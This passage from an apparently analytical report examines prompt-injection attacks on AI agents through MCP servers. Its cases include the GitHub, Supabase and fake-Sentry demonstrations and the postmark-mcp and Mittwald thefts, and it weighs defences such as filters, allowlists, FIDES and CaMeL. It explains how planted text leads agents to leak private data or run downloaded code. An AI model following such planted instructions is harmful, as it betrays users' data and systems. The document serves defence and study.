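The attacker needed to know very little, because the agent could find the private repositories itself. The same MCP server could both read those repositories and write to the public one. The data left through GitHub, so the attacker needed no server of their own, and a firewall that lets developers use GitHub would have let it through.

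By default, Claude Desktop asked the user to confirm individual tool calls. A careful user would have seen requests to read private repositories and open a pull request, neither of which was needed to answer the question. A user who had chosen to always allow these tools would have had no such warning. Invariant Labs states that many users choose this setting, while DevClass' *Researchers warn of prompt injection vulnerability in GitHub MCP* reports this as the researchers' suspicion. An operator could have found the pull request on the public page, and any record of the session's tool calls would have listed the private repositories that the agent read just before opening it. But the agent took all of these actions through the owner's account and within its permissions.

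This was a research demonstration on accounts that Invariant Labs had set up. It shows that the whole chain could work against a leading model of the time, but the post gives no success rate. Anthropic's newer models follow planted instructions much less often, but the permissions problem doesn't depend on the model. Invariant Labs stresses that the server's code had no bug for GitHub to fix.

GitHub (2025) narrowed the outbound channel that August, when it began checking for secrets such as access tokens in MCP calls that involve public repositories, on every type of plan. That would help against an attacker who wants passwords, but it would probably not have stopped this leak, since a salary and a project name don't look like credentials.

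### The Supabase support ticket (July 2025)

*Supabase MCP can leak your entire SQL database* (Willison, 2025) describes an attack on a support desk that used much the same chain. The security company General Analysis imagined a business that keeps its support tickets in a Supabase database. A customer submits a ticket containing instructions for an AI agent. Later, a developer asks Cursor, which can access the database through Supabase's MCP server, to list the latest tickets.

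The customer couldn't read other people's data because the database used row-level security, a set of rules about which rows each user may read. But Cursor was using an account called `service_role`, which is exempt from those rules. The model followed the instructions in the ticket, read private data that the customer couldn't, and wrote it into a text field of the ticket that the customer could read.

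The attacker had to know or guess that an agent would read the tickets and could write to them. Supabase's server supplied all three abilities, as GitHub's had. The outbound channel was the company's support system, which is designed to show text to customers.

The developer had asked for a list of tickets. With approval turned on, Cursor would also have asked the developer to approve the database queries, and a developer who read them could have noticed one that fetched unrelated private data. Supabase's *Defense in Depth for MCP Servers* (2025) advises users to keep approval on, but warns that they will tire of it and that part of a call may be off the screen. An operator who logged every query could have seen queries that read private data and, moments later, updated a ticket. The copied data would also have stayed in the ticket until someone removed it.

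Supabase and General Analysis described the same setup differently. Supabase objected to the claim that MCP "bypasses" row-level security, since the database still enforces the rules. But General Analysis was right about the result, because the rules don't apply to the account the agent was using.

The attack was a demonstration, and in the same reply, from September 2025, Supabase said that nobody had reported a customer losing data this way. Supabase had already added a read-only mode, which would have stopped the agent from writing the stolen data into the ticket. It still called injection its main concern in that mode. That concern is justified because a host that can read the database through one server may be able to send the data out through another.

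Supabase had also wrapped query results in warnings telling the model not to follow commands in the results, and had tested the warnings on weaker models. It reported that such measures reduced the risk but did not remove it.

### Fake Sentry errors (June 2026)

The best-documented MCP injection case of 2026 used Sentry, an error-tracking service, and went beyond a single laboratory setup. When a website that uses Sentry fails in a visitor's browser, code on the page sends Sentry a report. The code needs a key called a DSN, which is included in the page and lets anyone submit reports but not read them. Sentry documents the key as safe to publish.

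Tenet Security's *A Fake Bug Report Hijacks Your AI Coding Agent* (2026) explains how an attacker can use that key to submit a false error report. The researchers made the report appear to contain Sentry's own advice on fixing the error, including a command to run. When a developer asked a coding agent to fix the problem, the agent fetched the report through Sentry's MCP server and ran the command. In the tests, the command downloaded and ran a harmless package that Tenet controlled. A malicious package could have read the developer's access keys and sent them anywhere the computer could connect to.

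Here the attacker had to know only the public key and that some developers ask agents to look into Sentry errors. The agent's ability to run commands provided the tool the attack needed, and usually the outbound channel too.

Pinggy, a network tunnel provider, reports that the agents fully carried out the attack in 85% of tests. It says most of the failures occurred because an agent asked for confirmation before running an unfamiliar command. In those cases the model had apparently obeyed the hidden instructions, but the attack failed because the agent did not have permission to run the command. Forkast reports that telling agents in advance to ignore untrusted data did not prevent the attack.

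A rate of 85% is far above both the 0.5% in the illustrative example and what developers report for their newest models. The user's request probably explains much of the difference. Someone who asks an agent to fix an error wants it to find instructions and carry them out. Tenet's planted text looked like those instructions, so an agent could follow it without departing from its task. In the GitHub attack, a user who asks an agent to look at a list of issues does not want it to publish their salary.

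Tenet Security found 2,388 organisations with exposed keys that would let an attacker submit text, but that figure doesn't measure how many of them have agents that read Sentry reports and can run commands. Tenet says more than 100 agents acted on the planted errors in "controlled testing". It also says it confirmed this at organisations ranging from a Fortune 500 company to independent developers, and Pinggy says those organisations consented. Dividing 100 by 2,388 would not give a success rate, because Tenet's text did not necessarily reach an agent at every organisation with an exposed key.

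According to VPN Central's *Agentjacking Attack Can Trick AI Coding Agents Into Running Hacker-Controlled Code*, the developer saw what looked like harmless diagnostics, and Tenet says it took no secrets. An operator could have found the false report in Sentry, the command in the agent's transcript, and the download in the computer's or network's records. None of these would necessarily have raised an alarm. The Zerberos Blog points out that an investigator's timeline would show a developer's account doing ordinary development work on the developer's own machine during working hours.

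But people who looked at the errors directly could see this payload. On 3 June 2026, staff at the software company Nutrient noticed alerts in their error-monitoring channel that read like routine maintenance instructions. The suggested command would have installed a package whose publisher name differed from Sentry's by one letter. Nutrient recognised the fake and published ways to detect it.

Tenet told Sentry about the problem that same day, so the alerts may have come from Tenet's research, or from someone else with the same idea. According to CPO Magazine's *Over 100 AI Coding Agents Taken Over Via New “Agentjacking” Attack*, it was unclear whether criminals had used the technique. On the evidence so far, the Sentry case is known only as a research demonstration that reached real organisations.

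According to Forkast, Sentry acknowledged the report the same day but declined to make a fundamental fix, calling the problem "technically not defensible". Sentry added a filter that blocks one specific string from the payload. This interferes with the second condition in the chain, but only until an attacker changes the string. Forkast also cites reporting that Datadog, PagerDuty and Jira have the same weakness, which is plausible because all three can pass on text that outsiders influence.

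### Two thefts that needed no obedient model

Postmark is a service that companies use to send email. In September 2025 the security company Koi Security reported that `postmark-mcp`, a package published by someone unconnected with Postmark, was copying its users' email. The package provided an MCP server for sending messages through Postmark. Its first 15 versions worked as advertised, but the next added a line of code that blind-copied the developer on every message.

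In this attack, the model correctly called the email tool with the recipient and text the user wanted, and the server added the extra address afterwards. Even an approval prompt showing the exact tool call could not have revealed the blind copy, because it wasn't in the call. The user saw an email go to the right person. The operator could have found the extra recipient in Postmark's delivery records, or by comparing the new version's code with the old one.

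An attacker like this needs far fewer steps to succeed. Once the victim has installed the update, nearly every email is stolen. By contrast, an attacker who can only plant text needs almost 700 independent exposures for an even chance of a single success, at the illustrative example's rate of 0.1% per exposure. The hard part for the package's developer was getting people to install and trust the server, which they achieved by first releasing 15 legitimate versions.

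This was a real attack on the public, though its scale is uncertain. The package had about 1,500 downloads a week. Koi Security guessed that a fifth of these were in active use, and so estimated that the attack affected roughly 300 organisations and thousands of emails a day. Download counts include automated copies and repeated installations, so the true numbers could be much lower.

The attack on the German web host Mittwald targeted ordinary server software and didn't require anyone's model to obey instructions. Mittwald offered an MCP server through which customers' AI assistants could manage their hosting accounts. David (2026), in *MCP Security Best Practices After the Mittwald Breach*, reports that an attacker found a flaw in the server, read the session tokens of customers who used it, and compromised 56 customer projects. A session token proves that someone has already signed in,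 so the attacker didn't need passwords. Mittwald believes the attacker used AI tools, but its only evidence is the timing of entries in its logs.

### How far laboratory attackers are ahead of real ones

Laboratory studies usually start with some of the conditions for a successful attack already met. Shaikh and Montaruli set up the malicious server themselves, put a secret within the agent's reach and supplied a tool that could send it out, and no person approved or refused the calls. A real attacker has to arrange these conditions or hope they already exist, so the study's 22.9% is best read as a rough measure of how often agents follow hidden instructions when most of the other conditions are met. Lee and colleagues assume an attacker who knows no more than a stranger posting a comment, but even they put the planted text where the agent would encounter it.

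Promptfoo, a company that makes tools for testing AI applications, notes a similar limit in Huang and colleagues' comparison of seven hosts. The researchers ran their four attacks in isolated local setups without real credentials. This was responsible, but it can't show what an attacker could have accessed with a stolen key or whether a company's monitoring would have caught the theft.

Other features of laboratory tests make attacks look less effective than they might be in practice. A criminal can try many wordings on a private copy of the victim's host before using the best one. They can also choose their victims, and may learn from a job advertisement or public code repository which tools a company uses. They can then wait for a request that suits the attack, as Tenet's researchers could with developers who wanted errors fixed.

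Laboratory success rates are therefore almost certainly much too high for a randomly chosen comment on a randomly chosen issue. But a low rate on a fixed set of attacks could be much too low for a patient attacker who has picked one company and copied its setup.

### What is known about attacks in the wild

Attackers are trying indirect prompt injection outside the laboratory. *Fooling AI Agents*, by Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, reports injected instructions on live web pages. Underhill (2026) reports in *Cybercriminals Turn to Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks* that criminals are developing tools to attack AI agents this way.

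The security company Check Point reported in July 2026 that detections of indirect prompt injection rose about fivefold between March and May, to nearly 1% of all the prompts it observed, according to a summary by SmarterArticles. A detection means only that software flagged some text, not that a model obeyed it or that anyone lost data. When real attacks are rare, false alarms can also make up much of the total. If the detector wrongly flagged one harmless prompt in 200, false alarms would account for about half of that 1%. A steady rate of false alarms wouldn't explain a fivefold rise, but a more sensitive detector, a change in customers or a wave of security testing might.

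None of these incidents is a confirmed crime in which text planted in an MCP tool response led a model to steal data. The GitHub and Supabase attacks were demonstrations, and the Sentry attacks were too, as far as anyone has shown. The two real thefts, through `postmark-mcp` and at Mittwald, did not require a model to follow planted instructions.

One explanation is that planting text is still an unreliable way to steal. It may take hundreds of exposures to succeed once, while using a malicious package or exploiting a server flaw works nearly every time. Criminals have little reason to choose the less reliable method, at least against agents running the most resistant models. The Sentry tests count against this explanation, since they suggest that a well-chosen pretext can succeed most of the time even with popular coding agents.

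The other explanation is that such thefts happen and go unrecognised. Researchers can find the code in a malicious package, and Mittwald had to repair a flaw and inform customers. But a company whose agent followed instructions in a planted comment may have only a list of permitted calls under an employee's name. Default logging would not keep a copy of the comment, and the company might blame the loss on a stolen password or a careless employee.

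The public record doesn't show which explanation matters more. This would be easier to judge if companies that investigate leaks routinely checked what their agents had read before the leak, and said in their published findings that they had checked.

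## Defences and who is expected to apply them

Operators can make these attacks harder even without better incident reports. Some defences are designed to detect the attacker's text before the model acts on it. Others limit the damage the model can do if it follows the attacker's instructions, on the assumption that it sometimes will.

### Checking tool descriptions

The most direct check is to show people what the model reads, as Invariant Labs asked hosts to do with tool descriptions. This soon becomes a lot of reading. Shaikh and Montaruli collected 125 harmless descriptions from ten public MCP servers.

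A host can detect changes to a server's tools by hashing each tool's description and parameters when it first connects, then comparing that hash with the hash of every later version. In the WhatsApp demonstration, the malicious server replaced a harmless description with a hostile one. The new description would have produced a different hash, and the host could have blocked the tool until someone reviewed it. But comparing hashes can't detect a description that was malicious from the start, because there is no change to find.

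A scanner looks for signs of an attack in the text. Shaikh and Montaruli built a simple one that needs no AI model, and ran it on the descriptions from their 45 attack scenarios and on the 125 harmless descriptions.

| Check | Attack scenarios rejected | Harmless descriptions flagged |
|---|---|---|
| Commands that mention a tool or web address | 20 of 45 | 6 of 125 |
| Encoded text | 0 of 45 | 1 of 125 |
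| More than 500 characters | 2 of 45 | 3 of 125 |
| Any of the three | 20 of 45 (44%) | 9 of 125 (7%) |

The check for commands made every detection, and the other two checks added only false alarms. Six of the nine false alarms were descriptions that directed the model to another tool on the same server. A security team could cope with nine false alarms from ten servers, but a user who gets a warning with almost every new server will probably learn to ignore the warnings.

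The 25 scenarios the scanner missed included payloads in invisible characters, which had never worked, and payloads in other languages, which had often worked. Others presented the instruction as a policy statement or put it outside the description. The test counted scenarios, so it doesn't show what share of successful attacks the scanner would have stopped. An attacker who knew the scanner's rules could also reword the payloads it caught.

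These checks scan only tool descriptions. The attacker's comment on issue 214 arrives later, in a tool response, so no improvement to them would catch it.

### Filtering tool responses

Trail of Bits' *We built the security layer MCP always needed* (2025) presents mcp-context-protector, a wrapper that sits between the host and a server and checks both descriptions and responses. It looks like any other MCP server to the host, so it works without changes to either program.

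When the user adds a new server, the wrapper blocks all of the server's tools and withholds their descriptions from the host. The user reviews the server's instructions, tool descriptions and parameter descriptions in a separate command-line program, and the wrapper saves the approved version. The wrapper later blocks any tool whose description changes, and blocks the whole server if its general instructions change.

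Users can also connect detection software, such as Meta's LlamaFirewall, to scan every tool response. If the detector flags the response about issue 214, the wrapper quarantines it and returns an error message to the host, so the model never receives the planted comment. The user can read the quarantined text and release it if it was a false alarm. Terminal codes start with a hidden character, which the wrapper can also replace with the letters "ESC" to make the codes visible.

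A filter on tool responses covers the entry point that checks of tool descriptions miss. The detector that Lee and colleagues tested stopped most attacks, but most of those that got through weren't visible in the agent's final answer.

Those attacks weren't designed to get past the detector. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) cites research in which attackers defeated one combination of trained defences every time and found twelve others about as easy to bypass. Some hostile text also contains little for a filter to recognise. A false statement that Priya has approved a request contains no command, and the fake Sentry reports looked like ordinary advice on fixing an error.

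The wrapper also can't see the conversation, because MCP is designed to keep it from servers. The wrapper therefore can't use one of LlamaFirewall's checks, which reads an agent's whole history for signs that the agent has strayed from the user's goal. Trail of Bits recommends building such a check into the host. It also warns that users will tire of reviewing servers that change often, and suggests that organisations give that job to security engineers.

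mbgsec's *We built the security layer MCP always needed* (2025), a blogger's response to the release, raises two practical objections. Developers would have to set up servers through the wrapper instead of the server stores built into their hosts. And since chaining several gateways isn't really feasible, they would probably choose one that also offers caching and monitoring. Microsoft's *MCP Security Gateway* specifies a broader product of this kind, which scans every call and response, limits the number of requests and keeps an audit trail. *ShieldMCP* and *MCP-Guard*, two of the 2026 research systems listed in *Labels Are Not Endpoints* (2026), also check MCP traffic. The NSA considers security proxies for MCP immature and advises caution in using them with sensitive data.

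### Limiting what an obedient agent can do

An operator can reduce the harm from an attack without detecting it, for example by giving the agent fewer tools. In a test of a defence called Tool Filter, the model removed every tool the user's request didn't need before reading any outside text, so an attacker couldn't influence the choice. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) report in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* that this cut successful injections on GPT-4o from 152 to 20 in the AgentDojo benchmark. It helps least when the user's task needs the same tool as the attack, such as an email tool when the user asks the agent to send an email.

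Operators can limit what the remaining tools can do by giving them credentials with few permissions. The NSA advises operators to deny MCP servers access to any files and internal networks they don't need, and to run each tool in a sandbox, which restricts its access to the rest of the computer. It also recommends grouping tools by the sensitivity of the data they handle, so that a tool for public weather data is kept separate from one that handles health records.

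Users can apply the same idea to whole sessions. The purchasing manager could have the assistant summarise the supplier's web page in a session with only the fetch server, then open a new session with the price list and email. An instruction on the page would reach a model with no access to private files. The weak point is the text the manager copies into the second session. If it includes the attacker's instruction, the model there will read that instruction as part of the user's own message.

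Closing outbound channels works even if the model follows the hidden instructions and every tool is available. The NSA recommends sending outgoing traffic through a proxy that permits only specific addresses and methods. *Signed, Sealed, Leaked* (Aun, Alhartomi and colleagues, 2026) tested a list of permitted destinations against 91 versions of malicious MCP tools. The list stopped all 71 that sent data to the attacker's own server, but none of the 20 that sent it to a permitted destination. The researchers chose this mix, so the results don't measure what share of real attacks a list would stop. The GitHub attack would have passed because it also sent data to a permitted destination.

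Aun and colleagues also tested Meta's MCPGuard-Dynamic, which restricts the files and destinations a tool can use. They wrote a text-recognition tool that did its advertised job but secretly kept a salary sheet from an earlier call. When the user later sent it an invoice, the tool added the salary sheet to its request to the permitted text-recognition service. MCPGuard-Dynamic allowed this in every trial because it controls where data goes but doesn't track which data a request contains. The tool also carried a valid digital signature, which proves who published a program, not what the program does.

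Their own solution runs each call in fresh copies of the tool and gives each copy only the data its destination is allowed to receive. They detected no leaks in 153 attack runs, compared with leaks in 5.9–74.5% of runs under the other defences and a reduced version of their system. The system would have contained a package like `postmark-mcp` only if the operator's rules had treated the developer's address as a separate, unauthorised recipient. It also leaves ordinary prompt injection to other defences, because a model can misuse a tool that is not malicious.

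### Keeping outside text away from the planner

Microsoft's FIDES and a similar design called CaMeL both build on Willison's "Dual LLM" pattern. A planner model chooses the tool calls but doesn't normally read untrusted data, which may include an attacker's text. A second, quarantined model with no tools reads that data.

FIDES attaches two labels to every piece of data. The integrity label is either trusted or untrusted, and anything derived from untrusted data is untrusted too. The confidentiality label lists who may read the data. If A, B and C may read one document and B, C and D may read another, only B and C may read a text based on both. Before each tool call, ordinary software checks the labels against the operator's policy. Two typical rules are:

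- The agent may take a consequential action only if untrusted data did not influence the decision.
- The agent may send data only to people who are allowed to read it.

Here is one of the example tasks from Costa and colleagues, slightly adapted. A user asks the assistant to summarise the top three emails and send the summary to Dana on Slack. One of the emails contains an instruction to forward the user's mail to an outside address. The planner makes three calls:

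```text
read_emails(number=3)
query_llm(prompt="Summarise these emails", input=#read_emails_0)
send_message(to="Dana", message=#query_llm_0)
```

1. The planner has read only the user's request when it calls `read_emails`. The software labels the email text as untrusted, stores it under the name `#read_emails_0`, and gives the planner only that name.
2. The planner asks the quarantined model to summarise whatever is stored under that name. This model reads the attacker's instruction and may even try to follow it, but it can only produce text. The software stores that text as `#query_llm_0` and labels it untrusted.
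3. The planner calls `send_message`, using the second name in place of the message. The software confirms that the decision to send and the choice of recipient came from trusted data. It then inserts the summary and sends the message to Dana.

The instruction to forward the mail never entered the planner's context, so nothing prompted the planner to forward it. In an ordinary agent, all three emails would be in the planner's context by the third step. A strict policy would then have to block the message to Dana even if none of the emails were hostile.

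The attacker can still corrupt the summary. Costa and colleagues give the example of an email that makes the quarantined model return an empty summary. An attacker could probably make it leave out a contract deadline in the same way, as in one of the competition's scenarios. An operator could prevent this by requiring the message itself to be trusted, but then the assistant couldn't send summaries of outside email.

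Some tasks require the planner to learn something from the data. If the user wants a calendar entry only when an email asks for a meeting, the planner must know whether the email does. FIDES can restrict the quarantined model's answer to true or false, so the answer can't contain an instruction. The operator's policy can then allow that answer to influence the next step. An attacker could still cause an unwanted calendar entry, but couldn't make the planner choose an unrelated action.

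### What this protection costs

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES in AgentDojo with GPT-4o. Against an ordinary agent, 152 injections succeeded. Against FIDES with its policy checks turned off, 21 succeeded, because the planner could still open the untrusted text. None succeeded with the checks on.

That zero depends on correctly labelling data as trusted or untrusted. The researchers marked a type of data as untrusted if at least one attack in the benchmark used it. A real operator doesn't know in advance where attacks will come from, and might label as trusted a field that an outsider can edit.

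The next table gives the share of tasks each agent completed when nobody was attacking it.

| Type of task | Number of tasks | Ordinary agent | Ordinary agent with policy checks | FIDES with policy checks |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Office work | 40 | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 20 | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 16 | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 21 | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

Average completion, weighted by the number of tasks, fell from 82% for the ordinary agent to 52% for FIDES. Some of this loss came from GPT-4o confusing the names of stored data, and a stronger model, o1, raised completion on the travel tasks from 41% to 68%. Other failures were by design, because several banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and do what it says, which the policy forbids. Even a better model can't complete those tasks unless the user vouches for the file.

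Kolluri and colleagues, also at Microsoft, argue that this comparison is unfair to FIDES because the ordinary agent acts without asking for approval. Many real agents need approval before consequential actions. With the model o3-mini, an ordinary agent under that rule finished 24.3% of the AgentDojo tasks without asking for approval. FIDES finished 50.1%, and Prudentia, a newer version whose planner knows the policy, finished 59.1%. On the tasks they completed, the ordinary agent under the approval rule needed about 48 approvals and FIDES about 19. Fewer approval requests should also reduce approval fatigue.

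This argument works well for operators who already require approvals, but much less well for those whose agents run unattended. The researchers also assumed that a person would reject every injected action that reached an approval prompt, but the evidence on real users doesn't support this.

Prudentia can prompt the user to endorse a piece of data instead of approving each action. If an email lists ten jobs, one endorsement replaces ten approvals. But the user must spot any planted instruction before endorsing the email, because the planner will then treat all of it as trusted.

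In a second benchmark, Prudentia worked on simulated GitLab and Reddit pages. Attacks diverted an ordinary agent in 14.6–61.1% of cases, depending on the site and model. They never diverted Prudentia, which needed no approvals and completed at least as many tasks. The tasks were unusually favourable to this design, though, because the agent only had to post a comment or upvote a post and so never needed to read what outsiders had written.

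### CaMeL and the gap between agents

CaMeL is stricter than FIDES. Its planner writes a complete Python program from the user's request before any tool runs. Untrusted data can affect which of the program's branches runs but can't add a new step. This would have stopped the adaptive attacks on the email assistant, because a program written to summarise an inbox contains no command to send anything.

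Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, tested what happens when several CaMeL agents work together. A user asked the agents to send Julie a summary of job applicants on Slack. One agent read the applicant database, where the researchers had planted an instruction to email the data to an attacker. A coordinating agent had the data summarised and put the summary into its request to a third agent that handled messages. That agent treated the whole request as coming from its user, so it sent Julie the summary and also emailed the applicants' data to the attacker, even though each agent had followed CaMeL's rules. The same problem arises when a manager pastes a summary from one session into another, because the second session treats the pasted text as coming from its user.

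Across five models and 949 test cases per model, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL and 0.2% with it. Every attack that still succeeded passed from one agent to another. When agents had to pass outside data through a separate channel that the planner can't read, the rate fell to 0.0%.

Much of the improvement came from older models. The rate without CaMeL was 36.1% for GPT-4.1 but 1.5% for Claude Fable 5 and zero for GPT-5.5. On a separate benchmark of professional tasks, CaMeL reduced task completion by 21.6 percentage points on average, and by 13.4 for those two newer models. These reductions are much larger than *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) suggests when it describes CaMeL's task performance as "comparable".

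For an operator who uses a resistant model and expects only familiar attacks, CaMeL's drawbacks may therefore outweigh its benefits. It is easier to justify when an attacker has time to adapt and the agent can take irreversible actions. Its protection doesn't depend on whether the model was trained on similar wording.

### Bringing these designs to MCP

AgentDojo simulates its tools, and connecting FIDES or CaMeL to ordinary MCP servers would take extra work. MCP has no field for a server to declare how sensitive the data it handles may be (*Attested Tool-Server Admission*, 2026), so someone has to write the labels for each tool. CaMeL's planner writes its program before seeing any tool output, so it also needs to know the output's structure in advance. Peters-Gill and colleagues had to add this information to every tool description, and MCP doesn't require servers to provide it.

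An MCP server can use annotations to mark a tool as read-only, destructive or connected to the outside world. Model Context Protocol (2026) calls them hints that hosts must not trust unless they trust the server, since a malicious server could put the read-only annotation on a tool that sends data.

These designs also depend on the tools being trustworthy. Kolluri and colleagues explicitly exclude poisoned tool descriptions, which the planner reads as trusted text. An operator would still need to review and fingerprint descriptions before relying on FIDES or CaMeL.

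There is less evidence from MCP itself. *MCPHunt* (2026) measured how often agents connected to several MCP servers moved data where a policy forbade it. The rate was 11.5–41.3%, depending on the model. Added instructions reduced it to as little as 0.3% for some models but worked less well for others. Software that tracked sensitive data and guarded its movement also lowered the rate for the one model tested. These are rates of forbidden data movement, so they can't be compared with attack success rates.

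### Who should check the text

An operator using a standard framework gets none of this protection built in. Shaikh and Montaruli's code audit found no deliberate defence against poisoned descriptions in any of the twelve configurations it examined. None checked for embedded commands, false claims of authority, encoded text or unusual length, and none compared a server's current tool list with its previous one.

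Three frameworks have features that could give a false sense of security. Agno can ask the user before it runs a tool, but doesn't inspect the description that led to the call. smolagents can run code in a sandbox, which limits the damage but doesn't stop hostile text from reaching the model. Pydantic AI checks that a tool's parameters have the right structure, but a malicious sentence can pass this check because it is valid text.

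The researchers then sent five reports to four organisations, all of which rejected them:

| Recipient | Subject of the report | Reason for rejection |
|---|---|---|
| MCP's software kit | Tools that change after approval | Hosts should review tool calls |
| LangChain | Authenticity of data from servers | The library should pass on data unchanged |
| LangChain | Missing checks on the inputs to MCP tools | The software works as intended |
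| Microsoft, for AutoGen | Changes to a tool's definition | The documentation describes MCP servers as trusted |
| deepset, for Haystack | Poisoned tool descriptions | Users should vet servers before connecting them |

The MCP developers reasoned that protection comes from "host-side review of tool calls, not a notification the attacker controls". They are right that a malicious server can't be relied on to announce its own changes. The host also handles the user's request, the tool calls and the approval prompt, and Huang and colleagues found that MCP's weaknesses are concentrated on the host side. But Yao and colleagues found that many hosts don't review tool calls by default. Review also won't expose a poisoned description if the resulting call looks normal.

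LangChain's developers replied that their library "is not the appropriate place for any sort of validation". A library that silently altered data could break legitimate programs, and its developers can't know what would be suspicious in a particular application. The scanner's results partly support this position, because it missed more than half of the attacks and flagged harmless tools. These are arguments against compulsory filtering, but LangChain could still record fingerprints or offer an optional scan without changing any data. The reply also doesn't explain the second rejection, which concerned inputs to the tools rather than text from the server.

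Microsoft and deepset both assume that a user who connects a server has chosen to trust it. Developers make the same assumption when they install a software package, and FIDES and CaMeL rely on it too. The assumption is weakest for servers that change after installation, as `postmark-mcp` did. deepset agreed to explain the risk more clearly in its documentation.

Shaikh and Montaruli call the result an "accountability vacuum" in which every party points to another. But the replies assign the work, mostly to host developers and users. A fairer conclusion is that these people often don't know the work is theirs, or lack the tools to do it. The five rejections also concern attackers who control a server, so they don't settle who should protect an agent when an honest server returns a planted comment.

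### What the specification and official guidance ask

According to Penligent, a security vendor, the specification requires servers to check their inputs, control access, limit the rate of calls and sanitise their outputs. It only recommends that hosts show approval prompts, check results, set time limits and keep logs. The strict requirement to sanitise text therefore falls on the server, whose operator may be malicious, and even an honest operator can't meet it without knowing which sentences a remote model will follow as instructions.

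The November 2025 specification also gives users duties. One of its key principles is that they must "explicitly consent to and understand" access to their data (Model Context Protocol, 2025). The NSA quotes the specification's statement that MCP "cannot enforce these security principles at the protocol level". A host can ignore all of the specification's recommendations and still connect to every server.

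The Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* is mainly for people who build authorisation systems, run servers or evaluate security. It mostly covers attacks on authorisation, which have little to do with planted comments.

The NSA gives operators the most to do, including the sandboxes, separate zones and outgoing proxies described above. It also advises them to treat every output as untrusted input to the next step, even when it comes from a component they have already vetted, and to check it for planted instructions. Shaikh and Montaruli want the protocol to distinguish descriptions from instructions, frameworks to scan descriptions and ask about changes, and operators to choose models partly by their measured resistance to attack.

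The table below matches the main defences to the conditions an attack needs. The fourth column marks which defences fail if neither a person nor a program recognises that something is wrong.

| Condition | Defence | Who can apply it | Must someone or something notice? | Main gap |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Text is where a tool will read it | Connect only sources that outsiders can't write to | Operator | No | Inboxes, public trackers and the web are often the point of the task |
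| The tool's text reaches the model | Response filter | Host developer or operator | Yes, the filter | New wording, and false claims without a command |
| The tool's text reaches the model | Fingerprints and scans of descriptions | Host or framework developer | Yes, the software and usually a reviewer | Anything in a tool response |
| The model obeys | A more resistant model | Operator | Yes, the model | Adaptive attacks and plausible requests |
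| The model obeys | FIDES or CaMeL | Host developer | No, if the labels are right | Corrupted content and poisoned descriptions |
| A suitable tool is available | Fewer tools, or separate sessions | Operator or user | No | Tools that the task itself needs |
| The call is permitted | Narrow credentials | Operator | No | Misuse within the permitted range |
| The call is permitted | Approval prompt | Host developer and user | Yes, the user | Calls that look ordinary, and fatigue |
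| Data leaves | List of permitted destinations | Operator | No | Permitted services that the attacker can read |
| Nobody intervenes in time | Logs and alerts | Operator | Yes, staff or monitoring software | Payments and leaks that nobody can undo |
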